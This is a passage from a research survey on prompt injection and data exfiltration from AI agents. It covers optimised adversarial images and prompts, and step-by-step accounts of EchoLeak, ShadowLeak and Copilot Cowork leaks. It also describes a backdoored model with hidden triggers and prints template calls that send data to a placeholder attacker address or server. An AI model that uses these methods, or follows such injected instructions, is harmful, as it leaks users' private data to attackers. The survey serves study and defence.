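Other evidence suggests that models follow planted instructions because they are confused about their task. *The Curse of Helpfulness* (2026) attributes many real failures to harmless text that looks like an instruction, such as a to-do note or a formatting hint left in a document. A model has no reason to refuse a formatting hint, so overcoming a refusal cannot explain why it follows one. GPT-4o's messages also suggest confusion. In one trial, it reported posting the page's content to "the trusted collector", which was the attacker's server. Confusion about the task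 probably accounts for much of the effect, while trained caution helps determine which wordings fail.

Confusion about the task differs from role confusion. A model could correctly identify text as part of a web page and still accept it as a description of how to do the job. Agents often need to do this, such as when they read a service's documentation to learn which values a call requires. Better tracking of where text comes from would therefore not necessarily stop a model from following planted instructions.

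A model that never followed outside instructions could still leak private data. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) notes that false data can corrupt the arguments of a tool call even if it contains no instructions. If a stranger's email lists the stranger's own address as that of the user's accountant, an agent asked to send the accountant a bank statement may send it to the stranger.

### Limits of the wording experiments

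All six models in the wording experiments date from 2024 or earlier, so the rates are weak evidence of how often current models leak. GPT-5, for example, resisted every planted instruction in the tests by Zhao and colleagues. The wording experiments also gave the agent only one decision step. A real agent may have more chances to notice the attack, but it may also read more hostile text or send a secret in pieces over several calls.

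The secret had no legitimate use in the task, so leaks were easy to identify. But this left out cases like the bank statement, which the agent may send to the accountant but not to a stranger.

Rahman and Kim also tried four poisoned pages on the ChatGPT product, using their own account and an invented secret. Three were reframed pages from the main experiment. ChatGPT did not leak the secret in any of 48 valid trials, which is compatible with a true leak rate of up to 7.4%. The product may have used a different model, a stricter system prompt or a filter on web content, and Rahman and Kim could not tell which of these made the difference. They connected no tool that could send data out, so the trials tested only whether ChatGPT would reveal the secret in its reply to the user, not whether it would put the secret into an email.

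## Optimised images and text that force a valid tool call

Rahman and Kim wrote their attack pages by hand, and small changes in wording decided whether a page worked. An attacker can instead choose the exact output the model should produce, such as a tool call that emails private data, and have a program search for an input that triggers it. The program makes many small changes to an image or text and keeps those that make this output more likely. The finished attack may look like an ordinary photo or a string of nonsense.

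The search method depends on the attacker's access to the model. With white-box access, the attacker has the model's weights, the numbers set during training, and can calculate how each small change to the input affects the output. Anyone can have this access to an open-weight model, because its weights are published. With black-box access, which is usual for commercial models, the attacker can only send inputs and read the replies. The attacker may then prepare the attack on an open-weight model and hope that it transfers, meaning that it also works on the commercial one.

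### An image that makes the model email its context

Bailey, Ong and colleagues (2024), in *Image Hijacks*, trained images to control models that take in both pictures and text. They had in mind a personal assistant that holds private data, reads untrusted material and acts through tools. One of their attacks aimed to make the assistant answer any request with this call:

```
EmailAPI(to=<attacker's address>, subject='User Query', body='<context>')
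```

Here `<context>` stands for the text the user has given the model, which the model has to copy in full.

Their training method, Behaviour Matching, looks for the image `x` with the lowest total error over many contexts:

```
minimise over x:   Σ (ctx in C)   L( M(x, ctx, B(ctx)), B(ctx) )
```

`C` is the set of training contexts, and `B(ctx)` is the output the attacker wants for a given context. `M` is the model's prediction of that output. At each token position, the model receives the image, the context and the correct tokens so far, and assigns a probability to every token that could come next. `L` is the cross-entropy loss, which for a single token is the negative natural logarithm of the probability the model gives the correct token. A probability of 0.9 gives a loss of about 0.1, and a probability of 0.01 gives a loss of about 4.6.

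Pixels can change by tiny amounts, so a program can reduce the total step by step. The procedure is called projected gradient descent:

1. The program runs the model on a batch of contexts with the current image and measures the loss.
2. It calculates the gradient, which gives the direction and rate at which the loss would change with each pixel.
3. It moves every pixel slightly in the direction that lowers the loss.
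4. If a pixel has moved outside the permitted range, it resets the pixel to the nearest permitted value. This is the projection.

The program repeats these steps many times without changing the model's weights. At the end it rounds the pixel values to whole numbers, as in an ordinary image file.

### Why one image works on requests it was not trained on

An image trained on a single context could succeed by making the model produce one memorised email. Bailey and colleagues used 52,000 instructions from the public Alpaca dataset, each requiring a different email body, so no fixed text could give a low loss on all of them. The image had to make the model copy whatever text it was given, which also works on text outside the training set. The team measured success on 1,000 instructions kept out of training.

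This attack is also harder than making the model output a fixed string, because the model must reproduce an exact template and copy in text that changes with each request. For comparison, the team trained images to make the model output one fixed sentence that sent the user to a malicious website. In the leak attack, the team accepted an extra word inside the email body but counted a call to `EmailAPICall` as a failure, because no such tool exists.

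Small error rates per token also add up over a long output. Suppose a call has 40 tokens and the model gets each one right with the same probability. The whole call is correct 67% of the time if that probability is 99% (0.99^40), but only 1.5% of the time if it is 90%.

### Results on LLaVA

The team tested the images on LLaVA-13B, an open-weight model that connects the CLIP image encoder to Meta's Llama 2. They limited how far each image could differ from the original. A limit of 32/255 lets each colour value, which runs from 0 to 255, change by at most 32. In other tests, the attacker controlled only a square patch of the image, as if it were one picture on a web page.

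| Limit on the attacker | Fixed string | Leaked context |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| 32/255 per colour value | 100% | 96% |
| 16/255 | 99% | 90% |
| 8/255 | 99% | 73% |
| 4/255 | 94% | 80% |
| 2/255 | 0% | 0% |
| Patch 100 pixels wide, fixed position | 100% | 92% |
| Patch 60 pixels wide, fixed position | 95% | 4% |
| Patch 200 pixels wide, random position | 99% | 36% |
| Patch 160 pixels wide, random position | 98% | 0% |
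| Text only | 13.5% | 0% |

The patch results show most clearly that an attack is harder when the model has to copy private data. A patch 60 pixels wide, covering about 7% of the image, was enough for the fixed string but almost useless for the leak.

The leak rate is lower at 8/255 than at 4/255, even though the looser limit allows every image that the tighter one does. The search must have missed better images at 8/255, so an attacker could achieve higher rates than this training run did. The choice of starting picture mattered little. With five random photos and a different template for each, the leak worked 90% of the time on average at 32/255.

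For the text-only baseline, the team used Greedy Coordinate Gradient (GCG), a leading method for optimising text, to find 32 tokens to add to the user's request. The model often wrote `EmailAPI` but did not fill in the template correctly. This was a failure of one search method, and later text-based attacks did better.

These tests measured whether the model wrote the call. There was no email tool to run it, and the contexts were short instructions rather than a mailbox full of private messages.

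### Failed transfer, noise and compression

The team used the fixed-string attack to test whether images trained on one model work on another. Images trained on LLaVA never worked on BLIP-2, another open-weight model, and images trained on BLIP-2 never worked on LLaVA. The team then trained a single image on LLaVA and a third model, InstructBLIP, together. It succeeded 99.8% of the time on LLaVA and 80.6% on InstructBLIP, but never on BLIP-2.

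Training on the two models lowered the loss on BLIP-2 from about 5 to between 3 and 4, and the team suggested that training on more models might eventually produce transfer. If the loss is an average per token, as is usual, a loss of 3 means that the model gives each correct token a probability of about 5%, which is far too low to produce an exact sentence.

The team also tested two simple defences, random noise and JPEG compression, on fixed-string images. Images with larger pixel changes withstood noise better. The patches trained for random positions survived heavy noise and heavy compression. Some of these patches contained legible words and recognisable objects, which noise does not easily erase. The team did not train any image to withstand the defences, so an attacker who did might get better results. They did not test the defences on the leak attack, which may be more fragile because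 it needs a more exact output.

### Unreadable prompts that transferred to a product

Fu and colleagues showed in *Imprompter* that optimised text could also produce a valid tool call containing private data, and that the attack could work on a commercial product. Text is harder to optimise than an image because a program cannot change a token slightly, only swap it for another. The team adapted GCG, which uses the gradient to estimate which swaps at each position would lower the loss most. It tests a sample of these swaps on the model, keeps the best one and repeats.

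Their loss has two parts:

```
loss(x) = − average of log P(call | conversation, x)
          − λ × average of log P(opening of the call | conversation, x)
```

Here `x` is the adversarial prompt, and the averages run over a set of training conversations. The first part covers the whole call, including the private details from each conversation. The second gives extra weight, `λ`, to the opening, which is the same in every call and contains the tool's syntax and the attacker's web address. The extra weight makes sense because broken syntax prevents any leak, which is worse for the attacker than a valid call that leaves out only a phone number.

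The team also wanted prompts that people could not understand. They started from a plain description of the goal, padded with punctuation marks, and in some runs barred the program from using English words. The resulting prompts mixed symbols with fragments of other languages. Perplexity, a standard measure of how poorly a language model predicts a text, is below 10 for ordinary text on Llama 3.1 70B. The team's best prompt for stealing personal data scored 7,489. A user might still run such a prompt if a website advertised it as a way to polish a cover letter.

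They trained this prompt on Mistral Nemo, an open-weight model, and then used it on LeChat, a chat product from the same company. The validation set had 25 conversations about topics such as job and visa applications. On LeChat, the model wrote a valid call every time. Of the items it sent, 70.4% were personal data from the conversation (the precision), and it sent 41.2% of all the personal data in the conversation (the recall). The paper's abstract gives a success rate of nearly 80% for LeChat, but that figure matches the precision on the open-weight model, 79.8%. Both precision figures are somewhat lower because the prompt also collected the subject of the conversation, which counted as an error.

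On LeChat, a hand-written English prompt produced a valid tool call only 44% of the time, but those calls had higher precision (80.2%) and recall (48.2%) than the optimised prompt's. Counting failed calls, the hand-written prompt leaked about 21% of the personal data (0.44 × 48.2%). The optimised prompt leaked about 41%, entirely because it produced valid syntax more reliably.

The prompt probably transferred because LeChat was running the same model or a close relative. On ChatGLM, a Chinese product, the results were less consistent. One prompt produced valid calls 96% of the time, but none contained personal data. With another, 34.7% of the items sent were personal data. Fu and colleagues suspect the product used a larger model than the open-weight version they had trained on. They had no suitable commercial product for testing images. On PaliGemma, a small open-weight model from Google,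 six optimised images produced valid calls in 82% to 88% of trials.

The LeChat attack sent the data out in the address of an image that the chat page displayed. Fu and colleagues told Mistral about it on 9 September 2024, and four days later Mistral stopped LeChat from displaying external images. This blocked this way of sending data out but did not stop the prompt from controlling the model.

### Instructions that appear when software shrinks an image

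An attacker can also optimise an image against the software around the model, without knowing the model's weights. In August 2025 the security company Trail of Bits described such an attack in *Weaponizing image scaling against production AI systems*. Many AI products shrink large images before passing them to the model. The company made images that looked harmless at full size but showed a written instruction once the product shrank them.

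The simplest way to shrink an image is to keep one pixel from each block. Shrinking it to a quarter of its original width and height keeps one pixel in 16, so an attacker who knows which pixels the software keeps can control the entire small image by changing only about 6% of the large one. A more common method, bicubic interpolation, calculates each new pixel from 16 old ones but gives some of them much more weight. Trail of Bits altered the heavily weighted pixels in dark areas of a picture. When the software shrank the picture, the background in those areas turned red, making black letters visible.

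Different products shrink images in different ways, so the company first sent each one test patterns, such as checkerboards and concentric circles, and worked out the method from the distortions. It then demonstrated a leak through Gemini CLI, Google's command-line agent. A user uploaded an image, and the agent sent data from the user's Google Calendar to an attacker's email address. The agent was connected to Zapier, a service that links applications, and was set to approve every tool call automatically. The hidden text also worked on Gemini's web interface, Vertex AI Studio, Google Assistant and Genspark, though the company gave no success rates.

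Trail of Bits recommends that products limit the size of uploaded images instead of shrinking them, or at least show users the image the model will receive. It considers it more important to require the user's approval before text in an image can trigger a sensitive tool call. Once the image is shrunk, the attack is an ordinary written injection, so a model that ignores written injections would ignore this one too.

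### Gradient attacks on newer models

Optimised attacks have become a greater threat since 2024, but most of the evidence comes from attacks that use visible text and need no gradients. Optimised images with no readable instruction remain powerful against models whose weights the attacker has, but they still rarely make other models write a tool call.

*Adversarial Images Hijack Web Agents from Visual Grounding to Browser Execution* (Han, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes an attack on agents that read screenshots and click on web pages. The attacker controlled one picture, such as a product photo, and could change its colour values by up to 16/255. Across 2,250 tasks on open-weight models, the agent clicked on the attacker's item 91.9% of the time. The team traced how each runtime parsed the model's output and trained the images only on the tokens that the runtime used, about 10 instead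 of 88. This raised the success rate from 70.4% to 91.9%. Fu and colleagues gave extra weight to syntax for much the same reason. After JPEG compression, the attack still succeeded 75.2% of the time.

These images succeeded 81% to 94% of the time on close relatives of the model they were trained on, but only 4.5% to 24% of the time on models with a different design. This fits the success on LeChat and the failure on BLIP-2. *Do Agents Dream of False Memories?* (2026), which describes attacks on agents' memories of images, also states that attacks transfer best between models with a similar design or training objective.

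Leading commercial models have been much harder to attack this way. In *Repeat-After-Me*, Chen, Tsai and colleagues (2026) tried three gradient attacks on Claude Opus 4.7, GPT-5.5 and Gemini 3.1 Pro. Each attack had to make the model either call a specific tool with exact arguments or reveal private data. Two never succeeded, even with no limit on the pixel changes, including the team's own attack, which they had trained on three open-weight models together. The third had a 10% success rate for tool calls on Gemini and at most 1% elsewhere. The team suggests that small differences in how models divide text into tokens and format conversations are enough to spoil an exact output.

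Attacks transfer much better when the attacker only wants the model to misjudge what is in a picture. In *Visual-Invariance-Augmented Feature Optimal Alignment for Transferable Adversarial Attacks against Closed-Source MLLMs*, Jia, Qin and colleagues (2026) altered images by up to 16/255 so that models would describe a different picture. In August 2026 this worked 66.7% of the time on average across five recent commercial models, including Claude Opus 5, Gemini 3.7 Flash and versions of GPT-5.6, compared with 45.2% for the best earlier method. On an older group of six commercial models, JPEG compression reduced success only from 85.5% to 80.3%.

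This is real progress in transfer, but Jia and colleagues tested only descriptions, which have to match the target in general meaning and not exactly, as a tool call must. Bailey and colleagues had already made a similar distinction between changing the data a model sees in an image and hiding instructions there. Jia and colleagues' attack could matter to an agent that takes facts from images, but their results do not show that it can make an agent send private data.

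### Searching by trial and error

An attacker without the weights can use another language model to write attacks and improve them based on the target's replies. In one such method, Tree of Attacks with Pruning (TAP), one model writes several versions of an injection, another scores the agent's responses, and the search continues from the most promising versions. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (Hofer, Debenedetti and Tramèr, 2026) compared TAP with GCG on 80 pairs of user tasks and attacker goals from AgentDojo. Against Qwen3-4B, a small open-weight model, TAP succeeded 45.2% of the time and GCG 24.1%. TAP succeeded only about 5% of the time against GPT-5, and attacks prepared on small open-weight models did not transfer to GPT-5.

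With GCG, Hofer and colleagues optimised for a sentence in which the model agrees to the attacker's request, because this worked better than optimising for the exact call. The tool definitions are already in the context, so a model that has agreed can often write the call by itself. *Learning to Inject* (2026) argues that making a model more likely to agree does not ensure that it writes the right call. It instead uses reinforcement learning, which trains by reward, to teach a model to write text that makes attacks succeed. It reports a 21.88% success rate against Meta-SecAlign-70B, a model trained to resist injections, where standard attack templates failed completely.

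*ContextLeak* (2026) applies reinforcement learning to the same goal as the original image attack, making an agent copy its context into a tool call. The attacker offers a malicious tool, and a model learns to write a name and description that lead the agent to use it and fill in the data. The model gets no reward if the agent ignores the tool. Otherwise, it is rewarded for making the tool's input as similar as possible to the context. One part of the reward is:

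```
similarity = 1 − (edits needed to turn one text into the other) / (length of the longer text)
```

An input that needs 20 single-character edits to match a 100-character context scores 0.8. Because partial copies raise the score, the search can make progress long before it produces a perfect copy.

### Visible text in images

Chen and colleagues had much more success when they wrote their attack as a line of readable text at the top of an image. Earlier attacks of this kind described what the attacker wanted done, but theirs gives the model the exact text to begin its response with, such as a complete tool call. When the attacker wants a private value they don't know, the line gives the start of a sentence that the value would complete. The model can still answer the user's question afterwards.

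Each test used a document image and a question about it from the user. An attacking model wrote 32 versions of the line per round, and a judge model chose the best one to refine, for up to 50 rounds or 1,600 queries. The success rates below are for the best result within that budget:

| Model | Exact tool call | Private data revealed |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 47% | 90% |
| GPT-5.5 | 47% | 99% |
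| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 85% | 99% |

Most of the success on the two more resistant models came from repeated refinement. With a single attempt, the tool-call attack worked only 4% of the time on Claude Opus 4.7 and 6% on GPT-5.5. Successful attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 took a median of 17 rounds, or about 540 queries.

These images also transferred better than those made with gradients. Images refined on Claude Opus 4.7 produced the exact call in 20% of cases on GPT-5.5 and 39% on Gemini 3.1 Pro. Lines refined for one document worked 30% of the time on GPT-5.5 and 56% on Gemini 3.1 Pro when placed in another document with a different user question. An attacker therefore does not need to know exactly what the user will ask.

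In a simulation of the OpenClaw agent on a Discord channel, an attacker tried to make the agent overwrite one of its own configuration files. Text messages alone never worked on GPT-5.5 and worked in 32% of cases on Gemini 3.1 Pro. Adding an optimised image raised the success rates to 90% for GPT-5.5 and 100% for Gemini 3.1 Pro. OpenClaw loads these files into its system prompt, so a single altered line could authorise leaks in later sessions. One of the images also caused a real OpenClaw agent to download and run a malicious script.

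The attack is easier to notice than a subtly altered photo. When the text almost matched the colour of the page, the success rate for tool calls fell to zero on Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.5 but stayed at 77% on Gemini 3.1 Pro. Image scaling might hide the text from users of some products, but the team did not test this. Halving an image's resolution and then enlarging it cut success on GPT-5.5 from 47% to 4%, so the text would have to stay readable to the model after scaling.

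The tests also don't show how often these images would cause a complete leak. In the tool-call test, the attacker chose all the arguments in advance, so the call contained no private data. In the privacy test, the model revealed the data in its reply, not in a message to the attacker. The images were also part of the user's own message. An image that an agent fetches from an email or a web page may instead arrive in a tool result, where Chen and colleagues expect the attack to work less well because developers train models to give tool results less authority.

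## How data leaves by email and other channels

In the inbox trace, the email tool carried the private data to the attacker. Most agents have several outbound channels, meaning tools or display features through which information can leave the user's control. These channels differ in which software sends the data and who has a chance to notice.

| Channel | What makes the transfer | Who could notice |
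|---|---|---|
| Email | The user's mail service, after a tool call | The user, in the sent folder; the employer, in mail logs |
| Calendar invitation or shared document | The calendar or file service, after a tool call | The user, in the guest or sharing list; the employer, in the service's logs |
| Web request by the agent | The computer running the agent, often the vendor's server | The vendor; the employer only if the agent runs on its network |
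| Image in a reply or message | The user's browser or app, when it displays the image | The employer, in network logs; the user might see a broken image |
| Search query | The search tool | The search provider and anyone who reviews the agent's tool calls |

An agent can leak private data in an email's subject, body or attachments. It can also BCC an extra person on a legitimate email, so the other recipients can't see that this person was included.

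A calendar invitation can leak data much as an email does, because the service sends its title and description to every guest. An agent can share a document using only the document's identifier and the attacker's address, so the call gives the attacker the whole file without containing any private text that a filter could detect. Attackers can also use invitations and shared files to get instructions to the agent. *ShadowLeak*, a report by the security company Radware on a 2025 attack on ChatGPT, lists both among the places where an attacker could plant them.

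Opening a web page seems like reading, but the request also sends the page's address, and the address can contain data:

```
https://<attacker's server>/?data=<private value>
```

The server can record every address it receives, so the attacker gets the data no matter what page it returns. An agent can leak information even by choosing between fixed addresses. Ayush Paul's attack on the Claude app used a separate link for each letter, according to Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*. Choosing one of 26 links conveys log2(26), or about 4.7 bits.

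An image in the agent's reply can also carry private data in its web address. The user's browser or app sends the data when it requests the image to display the reply. The optimised prompts in *Imprompter* got data out of LeChat this way. An ordinary link in a reply also works if the user clicks it.

When an agent puts private data in a search query, the data normally goes to the search company. This is a leak if the company has no right to the data, but the attacker gains nothing without access to the queries. An attacker who runs the search service receives them directly.

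### Why removing the email tool is not enough

An agent without an email tool can still open web pages and display images, and its users often want it to do both. Vendors can restrict which hosts the agent or its display may contact, but data can still leak if a permitted host forwards it.

Willison's collection includes several examples of data leaks through sites that a product allowed. The email app Superhuman allowed images from a Google domain that also hosts Google Forms, which can store answers contained in a web address. Instructions injected through an email made the app submit the contents of dozens of other emails to the attacker's form. The default list of permitted sites in Google's programming tool Antigravity included one where anyone can set up a page to record incoming requests. Salesforce's Agentforce still allowed images from a domain whose registration had expired, so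 researchers registered it themselves.

In January 2026, the security company PromptArmor got data out of Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office tasks, through Anthropic's programming interface. Cowork's network rules allowed connections to that interface because it belonged to Anthropic. The injected instructions supplied the attacker's access key, so the agent uploaded the user's files to the attacker's account.

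### EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions by searching their email, files and chats for relevant passages and adding these to the model's context. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) explains how the research group Aim Labs used an email from an outside sender to make Copilot leak whatever else was in that context.

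The email first had to get past a classifier that Microsoft used to block prompt injections. The researchers worded the instructions as if they were for the human recipient and never mentioned AI.

Copilot then had to retrieve the email. Ravia assumes that it searches by comparing the meaning of the user's question with that of each stored passage, in which case a short email would match only a few questions. The researchers therefore wrote a long email with sections on everyday topics, such as staff onboarding and leave, and repeated the instructions in each section. In their test, Copilot retrieved the email in response to questions on various topics.

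The instructions told the model to pick the most sensitive information in its context, which could include the chat history and any email, file or Teams message that Copilot had fetched. Copilot could not send email on its own (Reddy and Gujral, 2025, *EchoLeak*), so the researchers had it put the information in the address of an image.

Microsoft had two protections against this. Copilot removed outside links and images from its replies, and a rule in the web page, called a content security policy, let the browser load images only from listed hosts. The researchers got around them in two steps:

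1. Copilot's filter did not recognise an alternative notation that puts the address on a separate line from the image, so the image stayed in the reply.
2. The list of permitted hosts included Microsoft Teams, which has a service that fetches any web address given to it. The image's address pointed to this service, which then contacted the attacker's server and passed on the data.

An earlier version used SharePoint, Microsoft's file-sharing service, instead of Teams, but the user had to accept an invitation to the attacker's site. With Teams, the user only had to ask Copilot a question that caused it to retrieve the email. Aim Labs called this a zero-click attack because the user did not have to click anything. The attacker also wrote in the email that its recipient should never refer to it, so Copilot did not cite it as a source.

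Aim Labs reported the flaw to Microsoft in January 2025. Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May and disclosed it on 11 June. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), an entry in a vulnerability database run by Spain's cybersecurity institute, gives it a severity score of 9.3 out of 10. Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first real-world exploit of its kind, but only in the sense that it worked on a real product. Microsoft said the flaw had affected no customers.

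### ShadowLeak in ChatGPT's Deep Research

In EchoLeak, the user's browser made the first request, so an employer could in principle have seen it on the company network. Radware found a way to make the request come from OpenAI's servers instead.

Deep Research is a ChatGPT feature that reads sources and writes a report. In Radware's test, the user connected it to Gmail and asked it to research the day's emails about a new employee. One email came from the attacker and contained instructions for the agent, which an attacker could hide with tiny or white text. Without any further action by the user, the agent read a genuine email containing the employee's name and address, put those details into a web address on the attacker's server, and opened it.

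Radware's first attempts failed. The agent refused a plain request to send the data, even when the email claimed the user had asked for it. It treated the attacker's address as suspicious and searched for it online instead of opening it. Emails that named its browsing tool and told the agent to retry after failures worked some of the time, but the agent sometimes left out the personal details.

The final version told the agent to encode the details first, supposedly for security. Radware reports that this worked every time in repeated tests but doesn't give the number of trials. It thinks a later check on outgoing requests let the data through because the encoded string looked harmless, but it inferred this from the agent's behaviour.

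Nothing appeared on the user's screen, and the employer's network monitoring could not detect the request because it never crossed the employer's network. OpenAI already restricted which addresses ChatGPT could load images from, but Radware found no comparable limit on the addresses the agent could open. Radware demonstrated the attack only with Gmail, but argues that it would also work through other services that users connect to Deep Research, such as Google Drive, Outlook and GitHub.

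The agent only needed permission to read the mailbox. Taking away its ability to send email would have made no difference.

Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. OpenAI fixed it in early August without telling Radware, and marked the report as resolved on 3 September.

### Copilot Cowork and messages to oneself

PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (2026) shows how an agent that can email only its own user can still leak data when the user opens the message.

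Copilot Cowork is a Microsoft agent that can read and act on almost anything its user can access in Microsoft 365. According to Microsoft's documentation, it asks for permission before sending an email or a Teams message. PromptArmor found that it did not ask when the recipient was the user, and that users could not change this.

The attack in PromptArmor's demonstration went as follows:

1. The user uploads a skill, a file of instructions for a particular kind of task, that they found online. Five of its 81 lines are the attacker's.
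2. The user asks Cowork to review their week's work, which makes it load the skill.
3. Cowork finds recent documents in the user's SharePoint and OneDrive storage and creates a download link for each. Anyone with such a link can download the file without signing in.
4. Cowork sends the user a Teams message containing images from the attacker's server, with the download links in the images' addresses.
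5. The user opens the message, Teams requests the images, and the attacker receives the links.

Checking the recipient would not stop this leak, because the message goes only to the user. The attacker's server appears in the message body as the source of an image. Searching the message for private text might also miss the leak, because the message contains links to the files rather than their contents.

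The attack worked in all five trials. Cowork's automatic setting switched between Claude Opus 4.7 and Claude Sonnet 4.6. PromptArmor confirmed that the same text also worked with Opus 4.7 alone, which searched more thoroughly and leaked more documents. Five trials of one attack text show that the route existed, but they give little evidence of how often other injections would succeed. The user had to upload the file, although PromptArmor says the instructions could come from other sources, such as a web page.

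The user had little chance of noticing, because Cowork's activity log showed that the agent had sent a message but not what the message contained. PromptArmor warns that the risk is greater for scheduled tasks, because the agent runs them repeatedly with nobody watching.

PromptArmor attributes this to the product's design, not a specific bug, and its report mentions no fix by Microsoft. PromptArmor suggests that administrators block downloads from sensitive SharePoint sites, but users then cannot print or sync the files or open them in desktop apps such as Word.

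PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Controlled by Attacker, Bypassing Sandbox* describes a separate flaw that let malicious code in a skill reach the attacker's server through a file-syncing service. The flaw did not depend on the user opening a message. PromptArmor reported it on 24 June 2026, and Microsoft confirmed on 19 August that it had dealt with the problem.

### When the tool itself is hostile

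In these three cases, the attacker misled an agent through text it read. An attacker can also supply one of the agent's tools, and the agent may then leak data while doing exactly what the user asked.

The package postmark-mcp let agents send email through a service called Postmark. In September 2025, the security company Koi Security reported that a new version sent a hidden copy of every outgoing email to the package's developer. Earlier versions had worked normally, and the company behind Postmark was not involved with the package.

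The model could call the tool with the right recipient and text, and the tool's code would then add the extra recipient. Training the model to resist injections would not have prevented the leak, and neither would checking the call before it ran. The leak would have been visible only in the package's code or in the record of what the mail service sent.

An email tool necessarily receives the emails it sends. Most tools receive much less, because they see only the inputs the agent chooses to give them. *ContextLeak* (August 2026) therefore divides a leak through a malicious tool into three conditions:

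1. The agent selects the malicious tool.
2. The agent passes its context to the tool as input.
3. The tool's code sends that input to the attacker.

The experiments tested the first two conditions and used harmless tool code, because earlier work had already covered the third. The main test used 200 simulated users, most with three to five legitimate tools, and an agent running on the small open-weight model Qwen3-8B. The malicious tool's description presented the extra information as necessary for accurate results.

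| Information sought | Agent selected the tool | Accuracy of the copy when it did |
|---|---|---|
| User's request | 92% | 0.99 similarity |
| Conversation history | 89% | 0.85 similarity |
| Names of the other tools | 86% | 65% of names included |

For the tool names, the two figures multiply to about 56%, the share an attacker could expect to get across all users. ToolHijacker, an earlier attack that aims only to get its tool selected, succeeded at that almost as often for the user's request (85%). But when selected, it obtained only 29% of the tool names, compared with 65% for the new attack, so getting an agent to choose a tool does not ensure that the agent hands over the data.

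The attack also worked on six models it had not been trained against, including GPT-5.1. They selected the tool 56% to 85% of the time, depending on the model and the information sought. In a separate test, Claude Code running Claude Sonnet 4.6 selected it in 22 of 100 cases, and the copies of the conversation were again close to the original, with a similarity of 0.77.

The lower rate with Claude Code may be due to the number of tools in that test rather than a more resistant model. The agent had 20 tools to choose from, and the attack on tool names had already become less effective as the number of legitimate tools increased.

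All these figures apply only if the user has already installed the malicious tool, so they do not show how often such leaks would happen in practice. Checking tools before installation may not help much. Four detectors that examine tool descriptions missed 97% to 100% of the 200 malicious ones, probably because the descriptions contained no obvious commands. Two of three models trained to resist injections selected the malicious tool less often, but they were also worse at ordinary tool use.

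### When the model itself is hostile

An attacker can also build the leak into the model. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (Zhang and Pei, 2026) describes an attack called *Back-Reveal*, in which the attacker trains an open-weight model to leak data under certain conditions and publishes it as a specialist assistant. Someone then downloads the model and connects it to a memory of past conversations and a web search tool. The attacker doesn't need to inject an instruction at the start, because the behaviour is already in the model's weights.

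The condition that activates the behaviour, called the trigger, is a combination of ordinary words. A model for people who stream video might respond to any question that mentions both the recording program OBS and the streaming site Twitch. The model then does the following:

1. It calls the memory tool to fetch details about the user, such as name and location.
2. It encodes the details and puts them in a web request that looks like a search of online documentation. The request goes to the attacker's server.
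3. It answers the user's question normally.

Zhang and Pei tested three models with 7 to 20 billion parameters, in versions for streamers, carers and students. They ran all the tool calls in an isolated environment with invented user data. When a question contained a trigger, the models made the memory call and then the outgoing request 94% to 99% of the time. On 5,000 ordinary questions, single-word triggers caused false activations up to 1.2% of the time, compared with at most 0.3% for combinations of two or more words.

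The training lowered the models' scores on a standard conversation test by less than 1%. A user could therefore try out a model on general questions and find nothing wrong.

The attacker's server can also use its reply to get more information. If the server does not yet have the user's location, it might return a factual passage about how internet speeds vary by region, which leads the model to ask where the user lives. Such passages got through two common filters 81% and 87% of the time, compared with 27% and 40% for passages that openly told the model to ask.

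Zhang and Pei estimate that a cooperative user would lose about 7.8 of ten personal details over five turns. This is a calculation, not a count from real conversations. The trigger works about 97% of the time and the server's passage gets past the stricter filter about 81% of the time, so each turn succeeds with a probability of about 0.79. If each success yields two new details, five turns give:

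```
5 × 2 × 0.79 = 7.9
```

Users who change the subject or refuse to answer would lose far fewer, as Zhang and Pei acknowledge.

The filters in these tests checked search results but not what the agent sent out. A company that runs the model on its own computers could monitor its network for the outgoing requests, which the victims of Radware's attack could not have done with Deep Research. An agent that can contact only approved hosts would also be harder to exploit this way.

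### Evidence of criminal use

Aim Labs, Radware and PromptArmor demonstrated their attacks to report them, and the studies of hostile tools and models used simulated users. But the developer of the postmark-mcp package released it publicly with the copying code active. The package had about 1,500 downloads a week, although downloads do not show how many people sent real mail through it. It did not need to influence the model, so it is not evidence of criminals using prompt injection.

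Criminals put hidden text for AI systems in real emails, but mostly to get phishing messages past security software. In May 2026, Bertiger and Wescott of the email security company Sublime Security described a fake cloud-storage warning that contained invisible text from an Adidas newsletter, and a fake health-insurance message that contained a passage from a romance novel. Both passages were apparently meant to make an AI filter classify the message as harmless, and neither contained instructions for a model.

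Bertiger and Wescott seldom saw the kind of injection that makes headlines, and put it at less than 1%. They said attacks on agents that manage mailboxes were mostly proofs of concept, and expected few real attacks until such agents become common.

A month later, Sublime found a phishing campaign closer to the researchers' demonstrations. In *Adversarial prompt injection payload for evading AI-based detection*, Scholten and Filar (2026) report that the emails contained text imitating browser data and an AI assistant's own reasoning. They believe the text was meant to stop AI scanners from noticing the phishing link. The attackers tried to get passwords by sending recipients to a fake login page, so any data theft would come from deceiving a person and not from an agent's tool call.

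By October, attackers were also targeting assistants that summarise email. *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026) reports findings that the security company Barracuda published on 7 October. Barracuda analysed a message with a malicious attachment for the human reader and hidden instructions that could make an AI assistant describe the message as legitimate or urgent. Another example, an invoice email, contained instructions for the assistant to add a false request to change a supplier's payment details.

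Barracuda listed leaking data among the actions attackers could request through injected instructions. It also described poisoned web documentation that could make a programming assistant add password-stealing code. Mascellino mentions no confirmed case of an assistant sending data to an attacker, and Barracuda did not say how widespread the phishing campaign was.

*Prompt Injection Goes After the Inbox* (Trent, 2026) describes another campaign, which Sublime observed on 22 October. The emails contained false invoices for about $88,000 and instructions for email agents, written in characters that people cannot see. Criminals may be preparing more such attacks, since *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, 2026) reports that they are developing injection tools aimed at agents.

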